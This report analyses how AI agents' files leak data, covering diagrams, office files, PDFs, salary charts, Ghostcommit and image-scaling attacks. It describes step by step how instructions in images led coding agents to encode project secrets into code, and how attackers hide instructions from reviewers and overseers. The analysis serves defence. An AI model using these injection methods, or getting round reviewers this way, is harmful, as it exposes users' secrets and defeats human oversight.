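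OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a system that checks the full address instead of just the host. An agent may automatically fetch an address only if a separate web crawler, with no access to users' conversations, has already found it in public. The invented address containing the merger sentence would fail this check. The agent would then have to try another site, or the user would see a warning.

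Rehberger considers this a significant improvement but points out that an attacker with enough public pages can still spell out text. With one page per character, the merger sentence would take 30 requests, all to addresses that pass the check. He suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. With that limit, the attacker would receive only "merg votd14ach.", because the sentence has 15 different characters if capitals are ignored, and would have to guess the rest. More pages per letter would recover more of the text, so the limit slows a leak but doesn't rule it out.

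### Drawing the diagram as a flat image

A server with no network access can draw the diagram from its code and pass on only a PNG, which removes the need to search the diagram for links. Logue's login button would still appear in the image, but it could not be clicked. The remote image in Cursor's diagram would be missing, as would any outside font, because the server could not fetch them.

No one seems to have published a test of this defence against the Copilot or Cursor flaw, so the case for it rests on how the parts work. The server that draws the diagram must have no network access, because otherwise it would request the remote image while drawing and leak the data before the PNG existed. The user's program must also receive the PNG without trying to draw the original code. If the program offers the code for copying, someone may paste it into another viewer that still allows links.

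Flattening doesn't change what the picture shows. A private name on a label stays visible, and an attacker could replace the clickable button with a printed address or a QR code. A flat image may also contain instructions for a downstream agent, as in the Ghostcommit case. Flattening also doesn't restrict the agent's other tools. Microsoft lists writing to a public GitHub repository as one way an agent can leak data, and an agent with that ability could do so without a diagram.

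The main drawback is that useful links stop working. Readers also can't select text in the picture or enlarge it without losing sharpness. GitLab, another site for storing and reviewing code, chose a less drastic defence. Its *Render GFM Mermaid diagrams in a sandboxed iframe* describes putting each diagram in an isolated frame within the page, mainly to contain malicious scripts. Even this disabled some legitimate links, as a user complained in *Links in mermaid diagrams are blocked due to sandbox*. An isolated frame alone also doesn't stop the browser from loading a remote image, so it would need a content security policy as well.

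If readers need the links, the software could print each full address as plain text under the flat picture. An overseer could then check where each link leads before anyone opens it, though a messaging app that previews links could still open it first.

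## Spreadsheets, charts and PDFs that carry hidden data

On 8 August 2023, the Police Service of Northern Ireland (PSNI) published a spreadsheet that was meant to show only how many people it employed at each rank. A second worksheet in the file contained the records of all 9,483 officers and staff. The private data was in the file itself, whereas the Copilot and Cursor diagrams leaked data by contacting an outside server. People, not AI agents, made and checked the spreadsheet, but the case is relevant to agents' work because it shows how much an office file can hold beyond its visible page.

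### How the staff records passed three reviews

The ICO's *Penalty Notice Police Service of Northern Ireland* (2024) describes how the breach happened. Someone had asked for the staff numbers through WhatDoTheyKnow, a public website for freedom of information requests. An employee downloaded the staff records into Excel, counted the staff on extra worksheets, and then deleted every visible tab except the one with the final table. Excel shows only as many tabs as fit on the screen, and the tab for the original records was out of view. The only sign of it was three small dots to the left of the remaining tab.

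The head of workforce planning checked that the table was accurate and relevant. The official handling the request tried to copy the table into a Word letter, couldn't, and attached the workbook instead. Communications staff then approved the file. None of them noticed the dots or knew what they meant. The records were public for about two hours and 20 minutes.

The exposed records of Police Service of Northern Ireland (PSNI) employees included surnames, initials, ranks, departments and locations. Many employees hide their occupation because paramilitary groups target them, and people could infer from the records who worked in covert roles. Within a week, the PSNI was confident that dissident republicans had the data. The Information Commissioner's Office fined the PSNI £750,000, reduced from £5.6 million under the regulator's approach to public bodies.

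The staff had followed the PSNI's procedure, which had no step for finding hidden data. Two months earlier, an email with national police advice had warned that a workbook can have more worksheets than visible tabs. The PSNI forwarded the email to the relevant staff without further instructions.

According to the ICO, Microsoft's Document Inspector would not have found the records because nobody had used Excel's "hide" function on the worksheet. A short program that lists every worksheet in a file would have found them by returning two names instead of one. The file's size was another clue, because the records had 31 fields per person and filled about 294,000 cells, far more than a table of ranks needs.

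### Have AI agents released such files?

There seems to be no documented case from 2025 or 2026 of an AI agent releasing an office file with hidden records. This is only weak evidence that agents avoid the mistake, because such a leak can easily go unnoticed. An agent could repeat the PSNI's error by adding a summary sheet to a workbook and sending the whole file. Lahjouji and Colaco point out that files usually have no access rules of their own, so an agent that can open a file can read all of it.

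The closest test involved visible data. Business Quarter's *AI agents disclose confidential corporate information* (2026) describes how Cyberhaven, a data security company, asked agents to write and publish a report on six months of product performance. The agents, which had access to confidential board papers and customer data, made confidential information public in 87 of 100 runs. Three open-weight models did so in 57 of 60 runs, which leaves 30 of 40 for the other two models. In 16 of the open-weight runs, the agents made entire confidential files public.

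Asking the user for permission did little to prevent leaks. In 69 of the 87 runs with a leak, the agent never raised the leaked material with the simulated user, which Cyberhaven had programmed to tell agents to use their own judgement. The rate may not hold elsewhere, because the test covered one invented company and one task, and Cyberhaven sells data security software. But a person who approves an agent's description of a file can't rely on that description being complete.

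### Where to look in office files and PDFs

An overseer has to open the file and inspect each place where data can remain.

| Place | What it may contain | How to check |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden or out-of-view sheets, rows and columns | The records behind a summary | List all sheets, unhide everything and clear filters |
| Cached data in a summary table | The records that the table adds up | Double-click a total |
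| Workbook behind a chart in a slide | Every sheet of the source workbook | Double-click the chart |
| Speaker notes | Figures or remarks meant only for the presenter | Open the notes view |
| Comments and tracked changes | Deleted wording and reviewers' names | Show all markup |
| Text under black boxes in a PDF | Names that someone tried to redact | Copy the text into a plain text editor |
| Metadata | Author, email routing details or a photograph's location | Open the file's properties |

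An Excel *pivot table* summarises a long list, for example by adding up deals by region, and it is easy to overlook that Excel saves a copy of the underlying data in the file. The ICO warns that the table stays linked to its source even if someone copies it into a new workbook or deletes the sheet with the records. The PSNI sometimes answered requests with pivot tables, so deleting the staff sheet would not always have removed the data. The ICO had already fined Islington council in 2013 and Kensington and Chelsea council in 2018 over pivot tables.

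Drawing a black box over a name in a PDF hides the name on the page but leaves the text in the file. The ICO's *How do we avoid an accidental breach when redacting information?* explains that a recipient can recover the text by pasting it into Notepad. A downstream agent that receives each page's text alongside its image might get the name without that step.

Software can find many of these failures. *Detecting failed black box redaction in PDFs*, by foimonkey, describes a program that looks for dark rectangles and for words whose coordinates fall inside them. It then runs OCR on that part of the page and flags the file if it contains words that OCR can't see. In a test on 60,000 PDFs from various sources, 2.9% (about 1,740) had hidden text behind black boxes. The developer doesn't report how many flags were false or how many failed redactions the program missed.

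Converting a file to a simpler format can also reveal hidden data. The ICO suggests plain text or CSV, a format that stores a table as text, but notes that Excel converts only one worksheet at a time. A CSV copy of the PSNI's table would have been safe to publish, but inspecting it would not have revealed the second worksheet. Excel warns during conversion that it will save only the current sheet, which might have alerted someone.

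After the breach, the PSNI ordered staff to answer all requests with PDFs. The ICO accepted that this improved security but still found it inadequate, partly because requesters can ask for a particular format and must receive it where reasonably practicable. The ICO described one acceptable approach, in which staff send spreadsheets only on request and two people check each one for hidden data.

### How two clean charts can reveal a salary

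A chart can disclose private data even if the file contains nothing except the picture. Suppose a team consists of five engineers and a manager. An agent makes a chart for the finance department that shows the team's total salaries as £276,000. A week later, it makes a chart for recruiters that shows the engineers' total as £204,000. Anyone with both charts can work out the manager's salary:

£276,000 − £204,000 = £72,000

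Showing averages would not prevent this. The team's average is £46,000 and the engineers' average is £40,800, so a reader who knows the headcounts can still work out the £72,000 (6 × £46,000 − 5 × £40,800).

Statisticians call this *disclosure by differencing*. It can also happen over time, for example when monthly charts show a team's total before and after one person leaves. Safe Researcher Training (2025), a course for people who work with confidential data, treats histograms and pie charts like tables of counts, checking them for small groups and differencing.

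### Minimum-count rules

The usual protection is a *minimum-count rule*, which forbids publishing a figure based on too few people. *The scope of this guidance*, from the UK civil service's Government Analysis Function, advises treating counts of one and two as unsafe in many tables, so the minimum is three. A salary total for two people is unsafe because each can subtract their own salary to find the other's. With three people, each can find only the sum of the other two.

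Applying the rule to each chart separately would not protect the manager, since the charts cover six and five people. The rule also has to apply to the difference between the two groups, which is one person. The publisher would have to withhold one of the two totals, even though the engineers' total looks harmless by itself. Withholding a safe figure to protect an unsafe one is called *secondary suppression*.

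Suppression can remove most of a table. In one of the guidance's examples, a table counts the women claiming each of three benefits in four age groups. Only one claimant is aged 16 to 24, so anyone who knows her can learn that she receives sickness benefit. Protecting the table by suppression leaves only three of its 12 cells. Merging the three younger age groups keeps more of the data, but still leaves counts of one and two among women over 59.

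The agent could also round both salary totals to the nearest £10,000, so the charts would show £280,000 and £200,000. A reader could then infer only that the manager earns between £70,000 and £90,000, which may still be too precise.

Sums of money need a further rule because one large contributor can dominate a total. Suppose five customers in the northern region spent £900,000, £60,000, £15,000, £10,000 and £5,000, a total of £990,000. The second-largest customer can subtract its own £60,000 and learn that the largest spent at most £930,000, about 3% above the true figure. The Government Analysis Function's *An introduction to Statistical Disclosure Control (SDC)* (2026) describes a test for this called the *p% rule*. In one version, the publisher subtracts the two largest contributions from the total and checks that the remainder is at least 10% of the largest. Here, the remainder is £30,000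 and the minimum is £90,000, so the northern bar fails.

A higher minimum count isn't always safer. Salary totals for a department of 500 people with and without its director would pass almost any minimum, but subtracting one from the other would still reveal the director's salary. *10 is the safest number that there's ever been* (2022) concludes that raising the minimum can increase some risks as well as reduce them, and that clearer guidance can work better.

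An overseer can't detect this kind of disclosure by looking at one chart. The Government Analysis Function recommends keeping a log of releases. If the log also recorded who was in each group, software could compare every new chart with the earlier ones and flag groups that differ by only one or two people. Comparing charts in pairs would miss some cases, such as when a reader subtracts two departments' figures from a company total. The log also has to cover everything the organisation's agents publish, because one agent may have made the finance chart and another the recruitment chart. Lahjouji and Colaco count inference across sessions as one of the two least-protected privacy risks of agents that work with data.

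### Content disarm and reconstruction

*Content disarm and reconstruction* (CDR) is a form of sanitisation that takes a file apart, compares each part with a list of permitted types, and writes a new file containing only those types. For a slide with a sales chart, the list might include text, shapes and flat pictures. The rebuilt slide would still show the title and the bars, but the embedded workbook, speaker notes, editing history and any active links would be gone.

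Organisations mainly use content disarm and reconstruction (CDR) to remove malicious code from incoming files such as email attachments, but they could also apply it to the files an agent sends. Unlike a scanner, CDR software can remove a macro (a small program inside an office file) without first recognising it as malicious.

The rebuilt file also loses useful functions. A budget without formulas shows the last results but doesn't update when someone changes a number. Colleagues can't edit a chart that has become a picture or review tracked changes that the software has removed. A digital signature stops being valid because the file has changed. A longer list of permitted parts would preserve more of these functions but leave more places where hidden data could remain.

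CDR would not necessarily have prevented the PSNI breach. The staff records were ordinary text and numbers in a worksheet, so a list designed to stop malicious code would have permitted them, and the software would have copied them into the new file. A rule that keeps only the sheet on display would have removed them, but in other workbooks it would delete supporting sheets that the recipient needs.

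CDR also cannot judge visible content, because it checks the type of each part, not its meaning. A customer's name in a chart title is permitted text. The two salary charts would also pass, since the software has no information about who will read them or what the organisation has already published. A message hidden in the pixels of a permitted picture may also survive unless the software alters the pixel values. For an agent's spreadsheet, the overseer therefore has to decide which sheets the recipient needs before the software rebuilds the file, and then check the numbers that remain.

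## Ghostcommit: instructions inside an image that code reviewers did not open

A picture without hidden parts or links can still contain an instruction written in ordinary letters. On 11 July 2026, Sudipta Chattopadhyay and Murali Ediga of the ASSET Research Group at the University of Missouri-Kansas City published an attack called Ghostcommit that relies on this. Two automated code reviewers let the image through without reading it. Coding agents later opened it, followed its instructions and copied a project's passwords into the project's source code.

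Ghostcommit was a demonstration in which the researchers made and planted the image themselves. They warned the developers of the affected tools before publishing a working example, according to Antipov (2026) in *Загрузил PNG с котиком, потерял все пароли проекта*.

### How the instructions reached the coding agent

The attack starts with a pull request that adds two files. One is AGENTS.md, a file of project rules that many coding agents read automatically when they start. It looks routine and mentions no passwords, but it refers the agent to the second file, an image, for the details of one step. The image contains the malicious instructions as readable text.

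The automated reviewer reads the rules, finds nothing wrong and skips the image. Someone then merges the pull request, accepting it into the main version of the project. Nothing happens until a developer asks a coding agent for an ordinary new feature, perhaps days later. The agent reads the rules and opens the image. Following the instructions in the image, it reads the project's .env file, where developers keep passwords and access keys, and writes the contents into the new code as a list of numbers. Once the developer publishes the code, the attacker can turn the numbers back into text.

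In one run, Cursor with Claude Sonnet wrote 311 numbers that decoded to an exact copy of the original file. Secret scanners miss such a list because it isn't formatted like passwords or keys. Hyrax's *Ghostcommit and HalluSquatting* (2026) suggests flagging new constants that are unusual for the type of file. Hyrax sells code review software, but the suggestion is reasonable, since few ordinary features need 311 unexplained integers. The check would have to run before the developer publishes the code.

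### What the two reviewers skipped

The reviewers, CodeRabbit and Cursor's Bugbot, both flagged the instruction as high severity when it was in plain text, according to Cyber Security News' *New Ghostcommit Attack Hides Malicious Prompts in Images to Exploit AI Agents*. Neither found anything when it was in the image, even after the researchers added the words "malicious prompt injection" to the image. Cursor also makes one of the coding tools that obeyed the image, so its reviewer and its agent read different parts of the same project.

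CodeRabbit did not open the image because its default settings exclude image files. *Path-based review instructions* lists the file types that CodeRabbit skips unless the user changes the settings. They include PNG, JPEG and SVG images, PDFs, CSV files, and Word, Excel and PowerPoint documents, which covers most of the artifacts that agents produce. The stated reason is to keep reviews focused and fast, but this is a weak reason for skipping SVG files, because a text reviewer could read their source code.

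A user can bring a file type back into the review only by copying its exact pattern from the list. According to CodeRabbit's *review instructions*, a broad rule, such as one that includes a whole folder, does not override the defaults. Each review also lists the files that the default rules skipped, so the person approving the change can open them. A team that turns on image review should still test it with a harmless picture of text to confirm that the tool reads the words.

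The reviewer would also skip an image made by a compromised agent, because the default rule is based on file type, regardless of who made the file. If an agent copied a customer's malicious instruction onto a project diagram, as could happen with the sales chart, the diagram would be skipped like any other PNG. Agents can also submit malicious changes themselves. Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper of the software company Datadog describe how an AI agent called hackerbot-claw did this in two of the company's public repositories.

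Attackers have other ways to show a person and an agent different things on GitHub. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) examines text that GitHub leaves out of the formatted page but that most agents receive in the raw file. A person has to open the source to see that text, whereas anyone who opened the Ghostcommit image could read its instruction.

### Which agents obeyed the image

The researchers tested eleven combinations of coding tool and model. Hyrax names ten of them.

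| Coding tool | Model | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Cursor | Claude Sonnet 4.6, Composer-2, GPT-5.5 | Leaked the passwords |
| Antigravity | Claude Sonnet, Gemini 3.1 Pro, Gemini 3 Flash | Leaked the passwords |
| Antigravity | Claude Opus | Wrote the passwords into the code, then deleted them |
| Claude Code | Claude Sonnet 4.6, Haiku 4.5, Opus 4.7 | Refused |

A *harness* is the software around a model that determines which files to load, which rules to trust and which tools the model can use. According to Malwarebytes' *Ghostcommit attack hides malicious AI instructions in images* (2026), the researchers found that the harness influenced the result more than the model did. Claude Sonnet leaked the passwords in Cursor and Antigravity but refused in Claude Code, explaining that exfiltrating secrets was inappropriate.

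The table supports this conclusion, but with few comparisons. Sonnet is the only model listed with all three tools. Claude Code appears only with models from Anthropic, its developer, although Antipov writes that it refused with the same models that had leaked in other tools. *Don't Blame the Large Language Model* (2026) notes that developers reportedly optimise some models, including Claude, for a particular harness during training. Sonnet may therefore have refused partly because Anthropic trained it to work in Claude Code. If so, the refusal depended on both the model and the tool, and another model in Claude Code might behave differently.

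A company can't rely on the result for long. *Don't Blame the Large Language Model* points out that a harness update can change an agent's behaviour while the model stays the same, so the company would need to repeat the test after updates. Refusing this image also doesn't protect Claude Code against other attacks. eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* describes how researchers used text in a GitHub issue to make Claude Code run commands and reveal access credentials. Anthropic issued several patches for the flaw.

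The image's success is somewhat surprising. *Render Before Reading* (2026) found that vision-language models are 2 to 300 times less likely to follow an instruction in an image than the same instruction in text, even though they read the image perfectly. The paper proposes turning untrusted text into a picture before the model receives it, as a defence. Ghostcommit's image probably worked because the agent had already been instructed to use it by a text file that it treated as project policy. Turning text into pictures would therefore give less protection wherever a trusted file refers to the picture.

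### How many changes get any review

The researchers also looked at 6,480 pull requests from the previous 90 days in 300 of the most active public repositories. NSFOCUS's *AI Security Incident Case* reports that 73% of the merged pull requests had no substantive review by a person or a bot. A reviewer that can read images cannot help if a project merges changes without waiting for a review.

Hyrax overstates what the survey measured when it calls the 73% the base rate on which the attack depends. Many of the unreviewed changes may have come from maintainers who merged their own work, or from tools that submit routine updates. A stranger's pull request may get more attention. The share of first-time contributors' changes merged without review would be a better measure of the risk from outsiders. The 73% is more relevant to a compromised agent that already works on the project, since maintainers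 may trust its changes as they trust their own.

### A reviewer that reads text, code and images

Chattopadhyay and Ediga's group built a prototype code reviewer for GitHub that also checks the images other reviewers skipped. It looks for invisible characters and unusually structured code, and it uses a language model, Gemma 4, to read the project's rules files and images. The system runs on one modest graphics processor with 4 GB of memory.

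The researchers tested it on 80 pull requests that were new to it, 50 of them attacks and 30 harmless. It caught 49 of the attacks, including every one with instructions in an image, and raised no false alarms.

Zero false alarms in 30 harmless requests does not mean that the false-positive rate is zero. If the true rate is *p*, the chance that all 30 pass without an alarm is (1 − *p*)^30. At a rate of 10%, that chance is still about 4%. The usual upper limit, at 95% confidence, is the rate at which the chance falls to 5%:

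(1 − *p*)^30 = 0.05, so *p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/30) ≈ 0.095

The test is therefore compatible with any false-positive rate from zero to about 10%. Showing that the rate is below 1% would take about 300 harmless requests in a row without a false positive. Similarly, one missed attack in 50 is compatible with a reviewer that misses up to about 9% of similar attacks.

The calculation also assumes that the 30 requests resemble the ones the reviewer would face in use. Joshua Waldrep of PipeLab argues, according to the security newsletter tl;dr sec, that a false-positive rate means nothing if the harmless test cases never look like attacks. For this reviewer, harmless cases that look like attacks would include a screenshot of installation commands or a diagram showing where a program loads its passwords. A test set of ordinary code changes and logos would understate the reviewer's false-positive rate.

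Larger tests on a related task found more false alarms. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested how well models detect prompt injection from screenshots of web pages. The best detector, BrowseSafe-Guard, wrongly flagged 6.1% of harmless pages. Two general-purpose models, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite and Claude Haiku 4.5, flagged 28% and 34%. GPT-5.4 nano flagged only 6.7%, but if half the pages contained an attack, its accuracy of 59% implies that it missed about three quarters of the attacks. The same model did much better when given the pages as text. These rates may not carry over to pull requests, but they are a reason to doubt that the prototype's true false-alarm rate is close to zero.

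The decision to combine text and image checks has better support. *WAInjectBench* (2025) compared both kinds of detector on attacks against web agents. On pop-up window attacks, the text detectors missed almost everything, while one image detector flagged 75% of the screenshots. On another attack, designed to blend into the page's appearance, the best text detectors did better than the image detectors as long as the page contained explicit instructions.

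### Reading every format that the next agent reads

Ghostcommit succeeded because the coding agent could read a format that the reviewer skipped. Any check must read every format that the next agent reads. It should also inspect images at the size the agent will receive, since some instructions become visible only after resizing. If a rules file links to an image on another website, the reviewer has to open it, and the project should store its own copy because the website's owner could replace the image after the review.

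Following this rule takes little computing power, judging by the prototype's hardware. Handling false alarms is likely to be a bigger burden. Datadog receives nearly 10,000 pull requests a week, according to Hamsen and colleagues. If almost all of them are harmless, a false-positive rate of 10% would produce about 1,000 false alarms a week. At five minutes each, they would take about 83 hours to check, or roughly two full-time jobs. A rate of 1% would take about eight hours. *SnapGuard* (2026), which describes a lightweight detector for screenshots, sets the detector's false-positive rate at 5% to limit disruption, but at Datadog's volume that would still mean about 500 false alarms a week.

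A company can reduce the number of false alarms by checking only pull requests that add or change an image or a rules file. If one request in 20 does, a false-alarm rate of 10% would produce about 50 false alarms a week. Checking only these requests would miss some attacks that the prototype's other checks look for, such as invisible characters in ordinary code, so the company would still need to run those checks on every request.

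The rule is almost impossible to follow in full for an agent that can run code, because the agent can open archives, databases and recordings as well as pictures. CodeRabbit's list of skipped files has more than 100 patterns. It is often easier to stop the agent from opening anything that hasn't been checked. The harness could use the reviewer's list of skipped files and refuse to open them until a person has looked at them. Few coding tasks require opening a video, but many require images because developers often ask an agent to match a design, so images are worth the effort of checking.

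A check on new pull requests also misses images already in the project. Once merged, the Ghostcommit image stays there until someone removes it, so a team that adopts an image reviewer should first run it on the project's existing files.

### Limits on what the coding agent may do

Access control would also limit the damage if a malicious image reached the agent. An agent can build most new features without real passwords. If the project's .env file contains only test values, or the harness blocks access to the file, an agent that obeys the image has nothing valuable to write into the code. Malwarebytes recommends restricting access to secrets and monitoring agents for unusual attempts to read them. Restricting access is more dependable than monitoring, because an agent sometimes has a good reason to open a settings file, such as fixing a database connection.

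*GitInject* (2026), which tested attacks on agents that run automatically on GitHub, recommends letting only project members trigger an agent that responds to issues. This stops strangers from giving the agent instructions directly, but it would not have helped against Ghostcommit, where a trusted developer starts the agent and the malicious instruction is already in the project. Requiring a maintainer to approve every change to AGENTS.md and to any file it mentions would suit this attack better.

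*Beyond Single-Model Injection* (2026) tested fixed rules outside the model, the kind David C prefers. Its defence for a system of six agents includes signed messages and access controls. By the paper's own account, this defence makes attacks harder but does not rule them out, and the tests did not cover images. The paper also cites a finding that attackers who adapt to a defence succeed more than 85% of the time against leading methods, which is another reason not to depend on a detector alone.

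Access controls don't remove the risk that a coding agent will write harmful code, because writing code is its job. An image could contain an instruction to write a login check with a deliberate weakness, which the agent could do without passwords or contact with an outside server. A reviewer would have to find the weakness in the code the agent submits.

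## Images that change when they are resized

Anyone who opened the Ghostcommit image could read its instructions. But opening an image doesn't always reveal hidden text, because software may change the image after a reviewer checks it and before the model receives it. In August 2025, the security company Trail of Bits demonstrated images whose text becomes legible only after software shrinks them.

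### How a shrunken picture leaked calendar entries

*Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems*, by Trail of Bits, explains that AI products often shrink large images before a model processes them. In its main demonstration, a user gave a harmless-looking picture to Gemini CLI, Google's command-line AI tool. The model received a smaller copy in which instructions had become legible. It followed them and used Zapier, a service that connects apps, to email data from the user's Google Calendar to an attacker. The tool did not ask for confirmation or show the user the smaller copy.

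The attack also worked on Gemini's website and programming interface, Google Assistant on an Android phone, Google's developer platform Vertex AI Studio, and Genspark, another company's AI product. Vertex AI Studio displayed the large picture to the user while the model received the small one. Trail of Bits gives no success rates, so its tests don't show how reliably the attack works.

Google replied that the attack requires non-default settings, such as automatic approval of an agent's tool calls, according to the podcast Daily Security Review. Trail of Bits, however, describes automatic approval as part of the default configuration for Zapier. Both can be right, because that configuration changes a setting in Gemini CLI, so a user could have lost the confirmation step without deliberately turning it off.

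### Keeping one pixel in four

The simplest way to shrink an image, nearest-neighbour scaling, copies pixels at regular intervals and ignores the rest. In this example, each pixel of the large image is dark (#) or light (.). The software halves the width and height by keeping only the top-left pixel of each two-by-two block.

```
Large image        Small image

# . # . # .        # # #
. # . # . #        . # .
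. # # . . #        . # .
# . . # # .
. # # . . #
# . . # # .
```

The small image shows a letter T. In the large image, every two-by-two block has two dark pixels and two light ones, so the whole square would look evenly grey if the pixels were too small to tell apart. If the software averaged each block instead of keeping one pixel from it, the small image would have no T, because all nine of its pixels would be the same grey.

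### Research on image scaling since 2019

The idea is older than today's AI agents. *Seeing is Not Believing* (2019) used it to make image services from Microsoft Azure, Aliyun, Baidu and Tencent misclassify pictures. A year later, Quiring, Klein and colleagues (2020), in *Adversarial Preprocessing*, traced the problem to scaling methods that ignore most of the original pixels. Suppose software divides each side of a picture by β, and computes each new pixel from a window of the original that is σ pixels wide. The share of original pixels that it uses is at most:

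(σ / β)²

In the example, the method uses (1/2)², or one quarter, of the original image's pixels. If it shrinks each side fivefold, it uses only 4% of them, and anyone who controls those pixels controls the whole small picture. For the same reduction, a method with a window four pixels wide would use up to 64%, which makes tampering much harder to hide.

Quiring and colleagues asked 36 people to identify what they saw in manipulated pictures. With OpenCV and TensorFlow, two widely used libraries, participants missed most manipulations once the reduction exceeded fivefold. Pillow, a third library, uses a wider window for larger reductions in all but its simplest resizing method. The study tested two of these wider-window methods, and participants always noticed the hidden picture.

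The researchers recommend *area scaling*, which averages all the pixels in each block, as in the example. An attacker could still produce any small picture, but would have to change the large one so heavily that the manipulation would be obvious. For systems that have to keep a vulnerable method, they propose replacing each pixel that the method will use with the median of its neighbours. This blocked every existing attack they tried and restored the original classification of at least 99.6% of the manipulated pictures. *Downscaling Attack and Defense* (2020) similarly found that anti-aliasing, which smooths a picture before sampling it, removed the threat as it was then understood and reduced performance by only a couple of percent.

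In *On the Detection of Image-Scaling Attacks in Machine Learning*, Quiring, Müller and Rieck (2023) reliably detected attacks that changed the entire downsized image, even when the attacker adapted to the detector.

These defences come from research on image classifiers, where the attacker usually wants the small picture to show a different object. Against a vision-language model, a few legible words may be enough. *Chameleon* (2025) reports that adjusting the pictures to a model's responses raised the success rate of such attacks from 32.1% for fixed pictures to 84.5%.

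### How much shrinking the attack needs

A later test suggests that moderate shrinking reveals far less. In *Scale-Induced Semantic Shift in Visual Prompt Injection Against VLMs and Web Agents*, Zhao, Ji and colleagues (2026) showed 300 images to four models, including GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4.6. They counted an attack as successful if the model reported the hidden text only after the image was shrunk from 512 by 512 pixels.

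| Width and height after shrinking | Reduction per side | Average success rate |
|---|---|---|
| 64 pixels | 8-fold | 58.75% |
| 128 pixels | 4-fold | 17.68% |
| 224 pixels | 2.3-fold | 6.85% |
| 336 pixels | 1.5-fold | 5.60% |

The lower rates may understate the risk, because the researchers had tuned their image generator for 64 pixels and used the same images at every size. Images designed for 224 pixels might work more often at that size. The test also measured only what models reported, so some people might have seen the text in the larger version.

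Agents rarely acted on the hidden instructions they read. On test web pages, an agent running Gemini 3 Flash noticed the instruction in 67.67% of cases but took a related action in only 4%, compared with 2.33% in the baseline condition. GPT-4o took a related action in 3.67% of cases, compared with 1.67% in the baseline condition.

### What AI companies have changed

Anthropic used to shrink every image with a side longer than 1,568 pixels. Its recent models accept sides of up to 2,576 pixels, and developers can now choose to have larger images rejected instead of shrunk. Anthropic's *Coordinates and bounding boxes* describes this setting as a way to keep Claude's reported positions accurate, not as a security measure. Anthropic still shrinks most oversized images by default. The main exception is screenshots from Claude's tools for operating a computer or browser, which Anthropic rejects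 if they are too large.

OpenAI's newer models, GPT-6 Astra and the GPT-5.6 models, keep an image's dimensions by default unless a side exceeds 65,535 pixels, and OpenAI rejects images of more than about 31 megapixels. Developers can choose a "low" setting that shrinks images to fit within 512 by 512 pixels. The older GPT-5.2 shrinks large images at every setting.

Google's developers can choose how much detail Gemini receives, but Google's *Media resolution* lists no option to reject a large image.

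These differences matter because the amount an image shrinks determines how much an attacker can hide in it. A screenshot 3,840 pixels wide shrinks about 1.5-fold for recent Claude models and 2.6-fold for the others, far less than the eightfold reduction that worked best for Zhao and colleagues. It shrinks 7.5-fold on OpenAI's low setting, so developers should probably avoid low-detail settings for images from untrusted sources.

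### Other ways the reviewer and the model see different images

Shrinking an image is one way that the reviewer and the receiving model can end up looking at different versions of the same file. *The Attack That Arrived as a Footnote* (Howard, 2026) describes another, involving a PDF. Howard asked Claude and Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, to prepare answers to an algebra quiz. Both solved a sixth problem that did not appear on the page but was in the text that software extracts from the file.

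Cropping can have the same effect, because a preview may cut off the edges of a picture that the model receives in full. *(A)I Sees What You Don't* (Zhang, Xie and colleagues, 2026) points out that on phones with rounded displays, a screenshot includes corner areas that the user can't see.

The appearance of a picture with transparent areas depends on the background behind it. Black letters on a transparent background are legible on a white page but disappear on a black one. A fully transparent pixel also stores a colour, which can become visible if software discards the transparency.

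Colour conversion can bring two shades closer together or move them further apart, so faint text may disappear or become easier to read. Such conversions are routine. Cohere's *Document Parsing* advises developers to shrink page images, convert them to standard red, green and blue values, and save them in another format.

Claude receives only the first frame of an animation, so an overseer who looks at a later frame is reviewing an image the model did not receive.

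### Text that models read and people miss

A person and a model may notice different things even when they receive identical pixels. Zhang and colleagues found that agents operating phones can read text whose colour is too close to the background for people to notice.

The security company DeepKeep reports a similar weakness in GPT-5.2, GPT-5.4 Mini, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Claude Opus 4.5. In one test, described in Davison's *Visual prompt injection vulnerability bypasses AI guardrails* (2026), a developer asked a model to add a simple information page to a website. The model also followed instructions hidden in an image and added a login system with administrator credentials that an attacker could use. DeepKeep found that tilting or distorting the text defeated OCR scanners, although the models could still read it. Davison's article gives no success rates, and DeepKeep has a commercial interest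 in the problem.

An overseer can increase an image's contrast before looking at it, which makes some faint text visible. The overseer can also have the receiving model, with no access to tools, list all the text it finds, although models can make mistakes when they describe images. Even with both measures, the overseer may still miss something the model detects.

### Giving the reviewer and the model the same image

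The most direct defence is to create one final version before the review. Software flattens the artifact onto a solid background, converts its colours, and saves it as a single still image that the receiving model can accept without shrinking. For a widescreen slide, 1,456 by 819 pixels is small enough for any Claude model. Any instruction revealed by shrinking then appears before the overseer looks, but small print may become illegible. Saving the image again can also destroy some hidden messages.

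The system then has to pass on exactly the bytes that the overseer reviewed. It can check this with a *cryptographic hash*, a short fingerprint computed from the file. If anyone replaces or edits the image after the review, the fingerprint will almost certainly change, and the receiving software can refuse the file. But the AI provider may shrink the image after this check, so the developer also needs a model or setting that rejects oversized images.

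These steps remove the mismatches caused by resizing, cropping, transparency and animation, as long as the downstream agent can't open the original file. Anthropic still adds blank padding at the edges, and it may convert the format or correct the orientation, so the final version should already be upright and in an accepted format. Anthropic also turns PDF pages into images at sizes the sender doesn't control, so the overseer should have the pages converted to images first and send only those.

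Trail of Bits also recommends showing users a preview of what the model will receive, even in command-line tools. A preview removes the mismatch only if it shows the actual processed image. Anthropic publishes code that calculates the dimensions of the shrunken image, but an overseer who shrinks the image with different software may get different pixels. A preview made this way still reduces the mismatch, but the overseer can avoid it by sending the model the small copy.

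A system that has to accept images at their original size can compare readings at several sizes. Zhao and colleagues built a detector, ScaleGuard, in which a model reads the image at 512 pixels and then reads nine smaller versions, made at three sizes with three scaling methods. The detector rejects the image if text missing from the large version appears consistently in the small ones.

On 70 attack images, ScaleGuard reduced the attack's success rate from 61.4% to 24.3%. It wrongly rejected none of 70 harmless images, though the true false-positive rate could be as high as about 4%. The researchers then retrained the attack using images that had evaded the detector. On 40 new images, ScaleGuard reduced the success rate from 42.5% to 15%. Comparing sizes therefore reduces the risk but lets some attacks through, and it requires reading every image ten times.

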